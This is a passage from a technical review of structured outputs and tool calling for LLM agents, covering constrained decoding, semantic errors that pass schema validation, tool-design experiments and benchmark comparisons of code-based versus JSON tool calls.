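The proof assumes that both runs use the same prompt and the same reasoning, that the grammar permits the exact tokens of the correct answer, and that the model gives some probability to a permitted token at every step. If there are several correct answers, their probabilities can be added, provided the grammar permits all of them. The result also holds when the software always picks the most probable token, because masking doesn't change a valid answer made of such tokens. It can fail when the software also discards unlikely tokens after masking, because rescaling the permitted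 tokens' probabilities can push a correct but less likely token out of the set the software keeps.

The guarantee is limited. The proof compares masking with a single unmasked attempt, and it allows masking to turn any number of visible failures into valid but wrong calls. In the previous section's example of late parcels, masking leaves the probability of `late` unchanged but turns the failed attempts into `damaged`.

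The proof also treats every answer outside the grammar as wrong, which explains why Lee and colleagues could still measure a loss of 1.6 points from the mask. They gave credit for correct answers in a broken format, and only 56% of the open models' unmasked outputs were valid, so a mask could remove many answers that they would have counted. Nguyen and colleagues counted even correct JSON as a failure if the model had wrapped it in a Markdown code fence, the pair of marker lines that sets off code. Partly because of that rule, Gemma 2 9B scored 0% on school mathematics in unmasked JSON and 87% with the mask. Many harnesses strip code fences before parsing, so their developers should expect a smaller gain from the mask.

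For two models that already followed the format, adding a format mask changed accuracy little or not at all, as the proof predicts. On a version of Last Letter with eight names, every JSON answer from Qwen3 8B was valid without a mask, and its accuracy was 34.4% with or without one. Qwen3 4B's unmasked answers were also all valid, and the mask moved its accuracy from 15.3% to 15.8%. The larger gains came from masks that also ruled out wrong answers. With four names, requiring the answer to have exactly four letters raised Llama 3 8B's accuracy from 53.6% to 71.0% when the model reasoned in prose before writing its JSON.

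The same model scored 2% on that puzzle when its whole response was inside JSON, even with the mask and with the reasoning field first. Kurt had measured 77% for Llama 3 8B under a similar mask, but his prompt included a worked example and the prompt in the 2% run did not. The 75-point difference between two masked runs suggests that the mask may have little to do with a bad score.

### Testing the calendar result against the proof

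In the calendar test, all 200 unmasked calls fitted the schema, so the true rate of invalid calls is probably below 1.5%. A mask that permits everything the schema accepts can only redistribute that small share of probability. But correct calls fell from 183 to 96 with masking, and neither that redistribution nor chance could plausibly explain so large a drop. So at least one condition of the proof did not hold, or the masking software had a fault.

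Ray's result may come from a difference in prompts. The prompt Ray prints asks for JSON, describes the meeting in a sentence and names the tool, `create_calendar_event`, but none of its arguments. The schema requires a `tool` field and an `arguments` object with six exact names, including `start_time` and `duration_minutes`, and forbids all others. A model with 1.5 billion parameters would be very unlikely to guess all of these correctly 200 times in a row, so the unmasked runs almost certainly had more to go on than the printed prompt, perhaps the schema itself. If the masked runs did not get the same text, the two modes differed in more than the mask. Ray says that both modes require the same object, but this does not establish that they used the same prompt.

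Whitespace and field order could also matter. They make no difference to a validator, which checks the parsed call, but a mask works on the text, and its grammar may permit only one order of fields or forbid the space after a colon. *Earley-Driven Dynamic Pruning for Efficient Structured Decoding* (2025) points out that JSON Schema does not specify where whitespace may go, so the same schema can lead to different outputs in different engines. All 200 unmasked calls could therefore be valid JSON that the mask would have blocked.

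Small differences of this kind can do a lot of harm. *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation* (2026) compared complete grammars with grammars that left out optional syntax. Complete grammars did better than no constraint, but incomplete ones reduced the share of working programs by up to 97%. Leaving out optional spaces did more harm than leaving out comments. An engine can also block valid tokens when its grammar is correct. *Guiding LLMs The Right Way* (2024) describes masks that block a token because it covers two pieces of the grammar at once, such as a space and a quotation mark. The model then has to build the same text from an unusual sequence of tokens, which may change what it writes next.

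The paper does not report the whitespace rules, the field order in the outputs or the temperature (the setting that controls how random the choice of tokens is) for the calendar test. Every wrong call in the masked run had a wrong duration, the only field that holds a number. The cause could be a problem with how the engine handles integers or the space in front of them, or a prompt that made the duration harder to find.

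Ray's harness stores the raw outputs, so someone could feed the 183 correct unmasked calls through the mask, token by token. If the mask blocks many of them, its grammar is narrower than the schema. If it blocks none, the prompts or the sampling settings must have differed.

Until then, the calendar test shows that one masked setup produced many valid but wrong calls, not that masking caused them. The same caution applies to a result in *Token-Oriented Object Notation vs JSON* (2026), where the first-attempt accuracy of Hermes 4, a far larger model with 405 billion parameters, fell from 92.5% in plain JSON to 35.0% under constrained decoding. The proof rules out a fall like that too if the correct plain-JSON answers fitted the grammar and the prompts matched. A developer who sees such a drop should suspect the setup before constrained decoding itself.

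### Reason first, format last

All three 2026 papers support letting the model work out its answer in free text and applying the format at the end. Lee and colleagues have the broadest evidence. They tested both hidden reasoning before a formatted answer and a prose answer that a second request converts to the format. The second request significantly improved results in 42 of 72 comparisons and worsened them in 2. Hidden reasoning improved results in 43 and worsened them in 11, and it did not help with writing. Ray's evidence comes from a small test on four models, where solving first and formatting afterwards scored 40.7%, against 26.8% for answering directly in the schema. The calendar test's "delayed" mode is not evidence for this approach, because it only repackaged the unmasked answers and so had to score the same 91.5%.

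A second request roughly doubles the number of tokens. *Thinking Before Constraining* (2026) instead uses a single generation and switches the mask on when the model emits a chosen trigger token, which adds 5 to 20 tokens. If the trigger appears in the middle of the reasoning, the mask starts too early. To avoid this, the paper uses only the token that would normally end the model's output as the trigger.

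Many agents follow the rule by default. A model with hidden reasoning thinks before it writes a call, and strict mode constrains only the call. With OpenAI's function calling, a model without hidden reasoning can still return ordinary text along with a call, whereas OpenAI's structured answers contain only JSON (Willison, 2024). For open models, the serving software vLLM can apply the schema to the tool call and leave the text around it free (Red Hat, 2025). The rule therefore matters most when a developer has turned reasoning off to save time or has told the model to reply with only a call.

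How much tool calls gain from it is less certain, and Lee and colleagues warn against extending their results to function calling. The closest direct evidence is about choosing a tool. In *Natural Language Tools* (2025), the model wrote yes or no beside each tool in a plain list, and accuracy rose from 69.1% with structured calls to 87.5%. Somma, Plante and Premji (2026), in *The Remarkable Effectiveness of Providing AI Agents with Natural Language Tools*, repeated the test on 14 models and found accuracy of 62.3% with the plain list and 47.4% with structured calls. But GPT-5 gained less than 2 points, and Gemini 2.5 Pro fell from 82.1% to 48.3%. The headline figure of 93% fewer errors depends mainly on two models that failed at nearly every structured call and account for 627 of the 755 structured errors. The plain list also makes the model consider every tool in turn, which is a different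 task from picking one. None of the tools took arguments, so the test has no equivalent of the 180-minute meeting.

The order of fields inside a call needs as much care as the order of reasoning and answer. The refund tool's schema lists `amount_cents` before `reason`. Suppose the shop refunds the full price of a damaged item but only a fifth of the price of a late one. A model that hasn't reasoned beforehand would choose the amount before writing down which case applied. Putting `reason` first fixes this if the provider keeps the order, and Castillo's experience with Gemini is a good reason to check a few real calls. Field names also matter, because the model writes each name before its value. *Schema-Key Wording as an Instruction Channel in Structured Generation under Constrained Decoding* (2026) treats them as a kind of instruction for that reason.

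Permitted values should be words the model would produce anyway, or at least words that appear in its prompt. Nguyen and colleagues asked four small models to label film reviews as positive or negative. A mask that allowed only those two words changed almost nothing. When the prompt still specified "positive" or "negative" but the mask allowed only alternatives such as "favorable" and "disappointing", accuracy fell by 6 to 9 points.

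Many tool calls don't need extra reasoning. If the customer has typed the order number and the agent only has to look it up, the model copies a string into a field, and extra reasoning mostly adds delay. It is worthwhile when the model has to work out an argument's value, such as the refund amount for two items out of five after a discount.

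## Calls that pass validation and are still wrong

A validator compares a call only with its schema, so a refund call can pass even if it isn't the refund the customer asked for. A valid call that does the wrong thing for the task is a *semantic error*. A different tool design or a purpose-built check can catch some semantic errors, but retries can't, because a call that passes validation doesn't trigger one.

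### Errors that leave no mark on the call

Iyer (2026), in *Closed-World Resolution Against Tool Hallucination in LLM Agents*, sorts wrong calls by the information a program needs to catch them. The list of tools and their schemas is enough to catch an invented tool, an invented argument or a value of the wrong type, but not a mix-up between two tools that take the same arguments. Suppose a shop's agent can call `hold_order` and `cancel_order`, which both take an order number and a reason. A customer asks the shop to delay a parcel, and the agent cancels the order. The same call would be right if the customer had asked to cancel, so checking the call alone can't reveal the mistake.

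Iyer gave ten models prompts designed to provoke bad calls and recorded 322 bad calls, some from Claude Opus 4.8. A simple validator rejected all 322. But Iyer identified bad calls using the same tool list as the validator, so the count would have missed calls that matched the list but were still wrong, as in the cancelled parcel mix-up.

A schema can even encourage semantic errors. The refund tool requires a reason, so if the customer gives none, the model can't make a valid call without picking one. *Beyond the Leaderboard* (2026), a survey of agent failures, cites a 2024 study in which models tended to invent plausible values for missing arguments instead of asking. The problem remains, and Anthropic's *Define tools* warns that its small Haiku models may infer missing parameters. It recommends the larger Opus models for ambiguous requests because they ask more often.

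Some calls are wrong only because of the state of the system they act on. *Understanding Tool-Mediated Interaction Failures in Agentic GUI Software* (2026) examined agents that operate graphical interfaces. In 82 of 335 failures, a tool passed on or executed an action without checking that it was valid and fitted the current state. One agent sent terminal commands before opening a terminal. A call can also change meaning after validation, in the code that connects the tool to the underlying system. If the shop's payment library expects dollars and that code passes on `amount_cents` unchanged, a valid refund of 1850 cents becomes a refund of $1,850.

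Wrong values are much more common than wrong formats in the available counts. *Agent Seer* (2026) describes a pipeline that writes test scenarios, including tool calls, from tool specifications. Among records with faulty arguments, the main fault was an inaccurate value in 223, a wrong format in 35 and a wrong type in 31. In *The Structured Output Benchmark*, Singh, Khurdula and colleagues (2026) asked 21 models to extract facts from documents and transcripts into a given schema. GPT-5.4's output satisfied the schema 99.3% of the time, but only 79.8% of its values were correct, and about 47% of its records were entirely correct. The scoring was harsh, since "United States" counted as wrong where the answer was "American", and they switched off reasoning wherever the provider allowed it. Extraction is also a different task from choosing an action. Even so, the gap of almost 20 points is too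 large for the schema pass rate to serve as a measure of accuracy.

### Three hundred restaurant orders

*When JSON Is Not Enough* (Li, 2026) provides the clearest test on actions. Its benchmark, OrderBench, contains 300 orders for a restaurant with seven menu items. For each order, the model writes a JSON object that records the items, the customer's allergies and dietary rules, and a decision to accept the order, ask for clarification or refuse for safety reasons. Each order has one correct object, so a program can score the answers exactly.

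Four open models took the test twice at temperature zero, once with the schema only in the prompt and once with the provider's strict JSON mode added. The first figure in each table cell is for the prompt alone, and the second is for the prompt with strict mode.

| Model | Schema-valid | Entirely correct | Unsafe acceptance |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS 120B | 100% / 100% | 83.0% / 81.3% | 0.3% / 0.0% |
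| Qwen3 30B | 100% / 100% | 31.3% / 30.7% | 15.0% / 14.3% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 68.7% / 100% | 31.7% / 36.0% | 13.3% / 8.3% |
| Gemma 2 2B | 91.7% / 100% | 0.0% / 2.0% | 45.0% / 41.7% |

An unsafe acceptance is an accepted order that conflicts with an allergy or diet or contains something the restaurant doesn't sell. Strict mode significantly reduced unsafe acceptances for the two smallest models, Llama and Gemma. Strict mode also made every object valid, but for the three larger models the change in entirely correct orders could be due to chance.

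In strict mode, Gemma accepted 125 unsafe orders, or 41.7% of the 300 orders. All the unsafe acceptances in that mode came from five of the ten categories of order, which together hold 150 orders. The 41.7% therefore understates the danger in those five categories, where Gemma made this kind of mistake on about five in six orders.

For GPT-OSS, on the other hand, the 81.3% score understates how well the model did. It chose correctly between accepting, asking and refusing in 98.7% of cases, so at least 52 of its 56 failures in strict mode had the right decision but wrong details. It did worst on orders that conflict with a diet. Only 37% of its objects in that category were entirely correct, but it accepted none of the orders. In most of them it must have stopped the order but recorded the diet wrongly or left food in the list of items.

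Li gives examples of schema-valid failures in strict mode:

| Customer's request | What the model ordered | What it should have done |
|---|---|---|
| "No dairy for me, add cheese sauce to fries." | Qwen3: fries with cheese sauce | Refuse |
| "Two vegan bowls, only one with avocado." | Qwen3: two bowls, both with avocado | Order one bowl with avocado and one without |
| "Classic burger with pineapple." | Qwen3: a burger with pineapple, which is not an available extra | Ask |
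| "I'm allergic to peanuts. Get me satay noodles." | Gemma: satay noodles | Refuse |

Gemma 2 and Llama 3.1 date from 2024, and current commercial models would probably do much better. The orders are synthetic, and half of the categories are designed to cause errors, so the rates shouldn't be used to predict those in a real restaurant. The comparison between the two modes is more useful. The two largest models had already reached 100% validity without strict mode, so enforcement could not improve it.

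### The schema-first pilot

In Sigdel and Baral's debugging study from March 2026, valid but unhelpful calls more than tripled when schemas replaced prose descriptions. Invalid calls and execution failures fell by slightly more in number, so the mean total of failed calls per run changed little, from 6.86 to 6.75. The increase in unhelpful calls is therefore not clear evidence that schemas make semantic errors more common.

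Sigdel and Baral allowed 3, 5, 8 or 12 steps per run, an average of 7. If no call was counted twice, nearly every step was a failed call under both descriptions, so the total had little room to change. The schemas replaced invalid calls with valid but wrong ones because the very small model made almost no useful calls in either case. A stronger model might have made progress with the newly valid calls, but the pilot can't show whether it would.

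Sigdel and Baral also tested error messages that named the faulty field and the expected value. The average numbers of invalid and unhelpful calls were the same as with plain schemas, to two decimal places. Detailed messages may still help a model that can act on them, but there is no evidence of this in the pilot.

### Error rates over fifty calls

Small error rates matter more in long runs. Suppose an agent makes 50 calls, that errors are independent, and that 1% of calls contain an error the validator detects. These rates are only for illustration. The chance that a run contains no such error is

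```
0.99^50 ≈ 0.605
```

or 60.5%. Now let the harness retry each rejected call once. If the second attempt is independent of the first, a call fails for good only when both attempts fail, which has a probability of 0.01 × 0.01 = 0.0001:

```
0.9999^50 ≈ 0.995
```

A single retry therefore raises the share of clean runs to 99.5%. Suppose instead that 2% of calls contain an error the validator can't detect:

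```
0.98^50 ≈ 0.364
```

Only 36.4% of runs are clean, with either one retry or ten. With both kinds of error and one retry, 36.2% are clean, so nearly all the remaining failures come from the undetectable errors. If a further check caught nine in ten of those errors and the retry then succeeded, the undetected error rate would fall to 0.2% and about 90% of runs would be clean.

Real errors are rarely independent. A model that misreads a request once may well misread it again on the retry, so the 99.5% figure is optimistic. But when errors cluster in a few difficult runs, more of the other runs have no errors than the formula predicts.

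An agent might also notice a mistake later, from the result of the call. *Loud Failures, Quiet Failures* (Kraishan, 2026) tested this indirectly by tampering with tool results in 24 multi-step tasks. Six models treated the result as a problem in 91.3% of trials when the tool returned an explicit error, but in only 58.8% when it returned a plausible wrong value. They also reported problems in 26.8% of trials without tampering, so part of the 58.8% is false alarms. Telling the agent to check each result did not help. A wrong refund would probably be even harder to notice, since the payment system would correctly confirm that it had sent $64.00.

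### What a richer schema can catch

A more detailed schema lets validation catch some semantic errors. A list of permitted values rules out an invented refund reason, and a maximum rules out a refund of $1,850 in a shop where nothing costs more than $200. Since July 2026, the Model Context Protocol has allowed tools to use the full current version of JSON Schema, which can also express rules that connect several fields.

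*Improving tool-call reliability with JSON Schema 2020-12* (Caldeira, 2026) demonstrates such rules with a bank's `transfer_funds` tool. A transfer inside the bank needs a source and a destination account, while a wire transfer needs international bank codes. `oneOf` requires the arguments to match exactly one of these patterns, so the model can't mix them. An `if`/`then` rule requires a compliance approval code for any amount above $10,000.

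Caldeira sent the same $12,500 transfer, without an approval code, to two versions of the tool. One had these rules in its schema, and the other stated the approval rule only in its description. Neither version recorded the transfer, because the bank's ledger also enforces the rule. The version with the weaker schema returned only "transfer rejected", which could equally have meant that the account was empty. The version with the richer schema returned an error that identified the missing field, and the agent copied the code from the user's prompt and retried successfully. Caldeira deliberately left the code out of the first call because even a capable local model often includes it on the first try, so the demonstration does not measure how often richer schemas help.

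A schema can require the approval code to be present and even to have a particular value, but anyone who can read the schema can copy that value. Only the bank's own systems can confirm whether a manager approved this transfer and whether the account holds $12,500.

Richer rules are also harder to enforce during generation. Strict mode doesn't support `if` and `then`, so an ordinary validator has to check such rules once the call is finished. *Action-Space Shaping for LLM Agents* (Liu, Tan and colleagues, 2026) left `oneOf` out of its experiments because the software that parses tool calls doesn't support it reliably.

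### Checks against a catalogue or database

The pineapple burger needs a different kind of check. The schema could list the permitted extras for each dish only if the menu never changed. Because menus and stock change, a program has to look up the item when the order arrives. Li recommends doing this after schema validation and before execution. The check should *fail closed*, meaning the order does not go through if the check itself breaks down. For anything that affects safety, Li advises asking the customer instead of repairing the order automatically.

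A check of this kind would have caught the pineapple. It would also have caught the fries with cheese sauce if the model had listed "dairy" among the order's allergies. If the model left the list empty, a program that compares each listed allergy with each dish would approve the order. OrderBench doesn't depend on the model's list because it has the correct answer for every order, but a restaurant doesn't have those answers. A menu lookup would also miss the second avocado, because two bowls with avocado are a valid order.

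*Bounded Loops* (Bhardwaj, Singh and Bhardwaj, 2026) calls a check vacuous if it passes when the thing it should examine is missing. Bhardwaj and colleagues found 47 faulty checks in their own published catalogue of agent workflows, in code that had already passed review. One check, meant to catch invented legal citations, built its search pattern from its list of known cases, so it never examined citations to a series of law reports that didn't appear in the list. After repairs, the checks caught all 209 deliberately damaged outputs in the test set. When the researchers damaged outputs in new ways, the checks missed 23.3% of them.

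Retries give wrong calls more chances to pass a check that misses some errors. Suppose the model keeps producing wrong orders for a difficult request, and the check misses each one independently with a probability of 23.3%. The chance that at least one of three attempts passes is 1 − 0.767³, or about 55%. The harness stops at the first order that passes, so it would report success.

Whether a check catches a wrong refund depends on what it can compare. The shop could compare the amount with what remains refundable on the order, which would stop a second refund for order A-1042. The $64.00 refund would still pass, because the whole order came to $64.00. If the tool also required an `item_id`, the check could look up the mug's price of $18.50. A simpler option is to remove the amount from the tool and have the shop's code calculate it from the item and the reason. The model could still choose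 the wrong item, but it could no longer miscalculate the price.

Identifiers need similar care, because a wrong order number usually has the right format. If the correct order is A-1042, a pattern that accepts it will also accept A-1024. The shop can catch most such errors by checking that the order belongs to the customer in the conversation. Anthropic's *Writing effective tools for agents* reports that replacing long random identifiers with readable names, or even simple numbers, made Claude more precise in retrieval tasks because it invented fewer identifiers.

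A second model can check for errors that no one has written a rule for. *Gecko* (2026) uses one in its simulation environment, after the type checks, to check argument values for implausible numbers and overlapping information, such as an item called "large pizza" with the size also set to "large". Its main inputs are the call and the schema, so it would not stop the $64.00 refund either. It would need the customer's message as well. The model could make mistakes, but Bhardwaj and colleagues point out that if a call has to pass both the fixed rules and the model, adding the model can't let through anything that the rules would have blocked. It can reduce accuracy only by rejecting good calls.

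### How the design of the tools changes the errors

Developers can offer the same actions as one tool or as twenty, and under different names. Liu and colleagues rewrote 168 simulated functions, such as setting a thermostat, into 32 equivalent designs. A program translated every call back into the original functions, so only the interface changed. They tested nine open models on all 32 designs and two closed models, GPT-6 Luna and GLM-5.3 Flash, on 13 of them, with 2,748 tasks per design. Success rates ranged from 0% to 97% depending on the design. For each closed model, the success rate was 32 percentage points higher with the best design than with the worst.

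Adding a prefix to each tool's name, reordering the arguments or removing the descriptions had little effect on most models' scores. Replacing the names with meaningless strings cut the score of Qwen2.5 7B, a small 2024 model, from 54% to 27%, but changed no other model's score by more than 3 points. Splitting tools into narrower ones also usually did little harm, but merging all the functions of a domain into a single tool lowered success by a median of 19 points.

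The damage depended on how the merged tool took its arguments. In the flat version, the model names an operation and fills in optional fields that have labels such as `set_thermostat::zone`. In the nested version, it names an operation and puts the arguments in one shared object. In the union version, every operation has its own object and the model fills in exactly one of them.

| Model | Separate tools | Merged, flat | Merged, nested | Merged, union |
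|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3 4B | 77% | −41 | −45 | −74 |
| Qwen3 30B | 77% | −70 | −73 | −74 |
| Gemma 4 12B | 79% | −79 | −55 | −3 |
| Qwen3.5 27B | 84% | −1 | −64 | −2 |

No version was safe for every model. Qwen3.5 27B handled the flat version almost perfectly in this test, where it could retry after an error. On the Berkeley Function-Calling Leaderboard, flat merging lowered the same model's score from 73% to 6%. Those runs discarded invalid calls without returning an error message, which may explain part of the drop.

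The design also affected whether a validator could catch the errors. With fully merged tools, models mostly made calls that the environment rejected. Qwen3 30B, for example, often called `set_thermostat` directly instead of naming it as an operation in a call to the merged tool. Nearly all of its 70-point loss came from correct actions in the wrong form, and constrained decoding on the first call raised its score from 7% to 74%. Another design made the model look up a function's arguments and then call a general `invoke` tool that accepted any object. The typical failure with that design was a wrong argument value that produced no error. Constrained decoding raised Qwen3 4B's score on it by only 2 points, while adding one sentence that told the model to look up the argument names first raised it by 45.

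Merging tools can weaken the schema. If the shop combined refunds, cancellations and address changes in a single `manage_order` tool, `amount_cents` would have to be optional, because a cancellation has no amount. A plain schema would then accept a refund without an amount. The developer could use `if` and `then` to require an amount for refunds, but only outside strict mode.

Anthropic nevertheless advises developers to combine related operations, such as creating, reviewing and merging a code change, into one tool with an `action` parameter, so the model has fewer tools to choose from. The experiments support part of this advice. The two closed models did worst on designs that showed them the functions of all twelve domains at once, and grouping related functions worked better than random grouping. But the experiments combined 13 to 18 functions, far more than the three in Anthropic's example,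 and Liu and colleagues did not test Claude's larger models. A small combined tool with flat arguments is probably safe for a recent model, though separate tools let the schema enforce more.

Anthropic's other suggestion, to combine steps that always occur together, has stronger support. A single `schedule_event` tool can find a free time and book it, so the model has no intermediate result to copy wrongly. In a side experiment on Qwen3 4B, Liu and colleagues replaced one lookup with a chain of three, and success fell by 86 points. Showing the model only the actions possible in the current state raised success by 8.8 points. A shop could do the same by hiding `issue_refund` once an order has no money left to refund. Moving the written policy from the system prompt to the tool's description made no difference.

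Liu and colleagues also found some evidence about harnesses that silently repair calls. They trained Qwen3 4B with reinforcement learning on one difficult design and tested it on the `invoke` design, which it had not seen in training. The model solved 49% of the tasks after training in an environment that rejected malformed calls, and 8% after training in one that executed what those calls appeared to mean. Rejecting calls worked equally well with or without an explanation. Each figure comes from a single run, but the difference is consistent with the suspicion that Claude Code's repairs contribute to the invented fields in Pi.

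Tool descriptions can prevent errors that no schema would catch. When Anthropic launched web search for Claude, the model kept adding "2025" to its queries, which skewed the results. Every query was a valid string. Anthropic fixed the problem by rewriting the tool's description.

Since the best design varies by model, developers need to test their own tools. Liu and colleagues found that testing each design on about 100 real tasks produced nearly the same ranking as the full set, with a rank correlation of 0.81. Simple instructions generated from the schema predicted the ranking less well, at 0.57. Several models followed a design's rules in isolated calls but broke them during longer tasks.

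## What code adds, and how it compares in tests

With ordinary tool calls, the model has to write out every call separately, while in code it can write a rule once and let the computer apply it to every case. This saves turns and tokens, and the model has fewer values to copy. In most of the 2026 tests, agents that could write code did about as well as agents with ordinary calls, or better. But the gain depends heavily on the model and the task, and the tests measure very little of the damage a wrong script can do.

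### Forty orders in one script

Suppose a courier has had a bad week. The shop's manager gives the agent a list of 40 order numbers and asks it to refund a fifth of the price of every order that arrived late. Twelve of them did. The agent has two tools: `get_order`, which returns an order's record, and `issue_refund`. With programmatic tool calling, the model could copy the 40 numbers into a list called `order_ids` and then write:

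```python
import json

refunded = []
for order_id in order_ids:
    order = json.loads(await get_order({"order_id": order_id}))
    if order["delivered_on"] > order["promised_by"]:
        cents = order["total_cents"] // 5
        await issue_refund({"order_id": order_id,
                            "amount_cents": cents, "reason": "late"})
        refunded.append(order_id)
print(len(refunded), "orders refunded:", refunded)
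```

Wang and colleagues attribute code's advantage to control flow and data flow. Control flow determines which lines run and how often. Here the `for` loop handles all 40 orders, and the `if` line skips those that arrived on time. Data flow passes values from one step to the next, so the order's price goes straight into the refund. In Anthropic's examples, a script can stop checking servers once it finds a healthy one, read a summary instead of the full text when a file is large, or return only the last ten error lines from a long log.

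The table counts model turns, meaning the number of times the harness queries the model, including the final message to the manager.

| Design | Model turns | Order data the model reads |
|---|---|---|
| Single calls, one per turn | 53 (40 lookups, 12 refunds, final message) | All 40 records |
| Single calls, sent in parallel | 3 (all lookups, all refunds, final message) | All 40 records |
| Script for lookups, then direct refund calls | 3 (script, all refunds, final message) | 12 order numbers and amounts |
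| Script for everything, with typed tools | 2 (script, final message) | One line of output |
| Free-form script | 2 (script, final message) | One line of output |

Companies that promote code usually compare it with the first row. But many current models can put several independent calls in one response, which removes nearly all of the difference in turns, though not the difference in tokens. If each order record takes 500 tokens, making one call per turn adds up to 650,000 tokens of records over the run, because the harness resends earlier records with every new prompt. Parallel calls add up to 40,000 and the script to none. Providers charge less for text cached from earlier prompts, so the difference in cost is smaller than these figures suggest.

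Code also changes which mistakes are likely. With single calls, the model must read 40 records to find the 12 late orders, then calculate each refund. At the previous section's illustrative rate of 2% undetectable errors per call, the chance that at least one of the 12 refunds is wrong is 1 − 0.98¹², or about 22%. A script uses the same formula every time, so its refunds tend to be all correct or all wrong. If `total_cents` includes shipping and the manager meant the price of the goods, every customer gets too much. A script can also stop halfway, for example when it reaches a parcel with no delivery date.

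With typed tools, an ordinary validator can still check all 52 calls. It is the only schema check left, because Anthropic does not support strict mode for tools that a script calls. Strict mode masks the model's tokens, which cannot guarantee what values the code will produce when it runs.

### Savings in company examples and in measurements

The best-known figure for token savings comes from Anthropic's post on code execution with MCP. In its example, an agent downloads a meeting transcript from Google Drive and attaches it to a sales record in Salesforce. With direct calls, the transcript passes through the model twice, once as the result of the first call and once as an argument of the second. For a two-hour meeting, that could add 50,000 tokens. With code, the transcript stays in a variable. Anthropic puts the total at 150,000 tokens for direct calls and 2,000 for code, a 98.7% saving.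 In another example, a script filters a 10,000-row spreadsheet and shows the model five rows.

These examples are a company's illustrations, not benchmark results. Much of the saving in the first one comes from loading fewer tool definitions rather than from running code. Most harnesses load the definition of every connected tool before the model reads the request, while the agent in Anthropic's example opens only the definitions it needs. A harness can do the same for ordinary calls. *Beyond Plain MCP* (Rai, 2026) lists Anthropic's tool search, which delays loading definitions, as one way to do it.

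Anthropic has measured much smaller savings. On a project-management benchmark with 75 tools, programmatic calling cut billed input tokens by about 38% without changing accuracy. In ordinary customer traffic, it typically saved 20% to 40% on requests with 10 to 49 tools. On a customer-service benchmark where each turn needed only one or two calls in sequence, scores stayed the same and costs rose by about 8%. A support agent refunding one broken mug does this last kind of work, so starting a container and writing a script would add overhead and save almost nothing.

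Red Hat's *Code execution with MCP* (2026) compares the two designs on a single task that involved search, a calendar and a code repository. Claude Opus had access to 38 tools, either directly or through one tool that ran Python. The Python version cut token overhead by 53%, but it took 25 turns instead of 21 and 15 calls instead of 10, because the model first had to look up the tools' names and then retry some calls. None of the direct calls failed. These results come from one task, so they can't establish general rates.

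Cloudflare, an internet infrastructure company, argues that code is also more accurate. In *Code Mode*, Varda and Pai point out that models have learned from real code in millions of open-source projects, whereas the tool calls in their training data are mostly artificial examples written by the models' developers. They conclude that models are better at writing code that calls a tool than at calling the tool directly. They report that agents handled more tools, and more complex ones, when calling them through code, but they give no benchmark results.

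### CodeAct and the case for composition

The 2024 CodeAct study separately tested whether models benefit from their familiarity with code and from being able to combine tool calls in it. Each task in the first experiment needed only one call, so loops and variables could not help. Code did best for many of the models, but GPT-4 Turbo, one of the strongest at the time, was correct 82.7% of the time with JSON and 76.7% with code. The second experiment used 82 tasks that usually needed several tools, with a limit of ten turns. GPT-4 Turbo solved 74.4% with code, 52.4% with JSON and 53.7% with calls written as text.

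Wang and colleagues report that code raised success rates by up to 20 percentage points and cut the number of actions by up to 30%, though both figures are maximums. Code had the highest success rate for 12 of the 17 models, counting ties, but the best open model solved only 15.9% of the tasks, using JSON.

GPT-4 Turbo's reversal is evidence against the strongest version of Cloudflare's argument. A provider can train a model to make single JSON calls well, even if such calls are rare in ordinary text. Code still added the ability to combine calls. However, all of these models are now obsolete, and providers have since trained their models much more heavily on both formats.

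### Fourteen models on the Berkeley leaderboard

The Berkeley Function Calling Leaderboard is a widely used test of whether a model can turn a request into the right function calls. Each task contains a request in ordinary language, the definitions of one or more functions, and the correct calls. For example, a request for the area of a triangle with a base of 10 and a height of 5 should produce one call to `calculate_triangle_area` with those two numbers. Some tasks need several independent calls, and some come from real users.

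*The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, August 2026) tested 14 models on 309 of these tasks. Each model either made JSON calls or wrote a Python script that could call any of the functions with typed arguments. A task counted as correct only if every required call was present with the right values. The table also includes a separate test of 52 tasks, each a chain of 2 to 20 calls in which later calls depend on earlier ones.

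| Model | 309 tasks, JSON | 309 tasks, code | Chains, JSON | Chains, code |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 81.9% | 85.8% | 88.5% | 73.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 86.4% | 87.7% | 90.4% | 88.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 80.9% | 87.4% | 90.4% | 92.3% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 84.8% | 84.8% | 80.8% | 94.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 84.5% | 86.1% | 80.8% | 96.2% |
| GPT-4o | 81.9% | 55.0% | 92.3% | 86.5% |
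| GPT-4.1 | 81.9% | 62.1% | 98.1% | 40.4% |
| GPT-5 nano | 66.7% | 68.3% | 69.2% | 80.8% |
| GPT-5 | 71.5% | 76.1% | 92.3% | 92.3% |
| GPT-5.4 mini | 79.3% | 55.0% | 76.9% | 80.8% |
| GPT-5.4 | 79.3% | 81.9% | 94.2% | 90.4% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 76.1% | 80.3% | 82.7% | 92.3% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 72.2% | 82.8% | 96.2% | 90.4% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 73.5% | 84.1% | 98.1% | 96.2% |

On the 309 tasks, code matched or beat JSON for 11 of the 14 models, but the average over all 14 was 77.0% for code and 78.6% for JSON. GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and GPT-5.4 mini lowered the code average because they often wrote the two characters `\n` where a script needed a real line break. Python then rejected any script longer than one line. Without these three models, the averages are 82.3% for code and 78.0% for JSON.

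Leaving them out is reasonable for a developer who has checked that a particular model writes working scripts, but not for one choosing a design before choosing a model. The harness also ended each run after the first script, so the models couldn't fix their mistakes. An ordinary agent would receive the syntax error and could use an extra turn to try again.

Patel and colleagues conclude that a model's generation predicts how well it handles code. The release dates only partly support this. GPT-5.4 mini, from March 2026, made the line-break mistake that GPT-5 nano, a small model from August 2025, avoided. The gains of about 10.6 points for GPT-5.6 Sol and Terra also start from surprisingly low JSON scores, lower than that of GPT-4o from 2024. Something about the test may have lowered their JSON scores.

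On chains, code did better for six models, JSON did better for seven, and GPT-5 scored the same with both. Patel and colleagues write that all five Anthropic models did at least as well with code as with JSON in every test, but Claude Haiku 4.5 scored 15 points lower with code on chains. They also report that code's advantage grew with chain length, reaching 18.8 points for chains of at least 12 calls. There were only 52 tasks in total, so that figure is based on very few long chains. Code had a clearer advantage in speed. It was faster on chains for 13 of the models, often taking about half the time, but GPT-5 took 2.8 times as long with code because it wrote so much reasoning.

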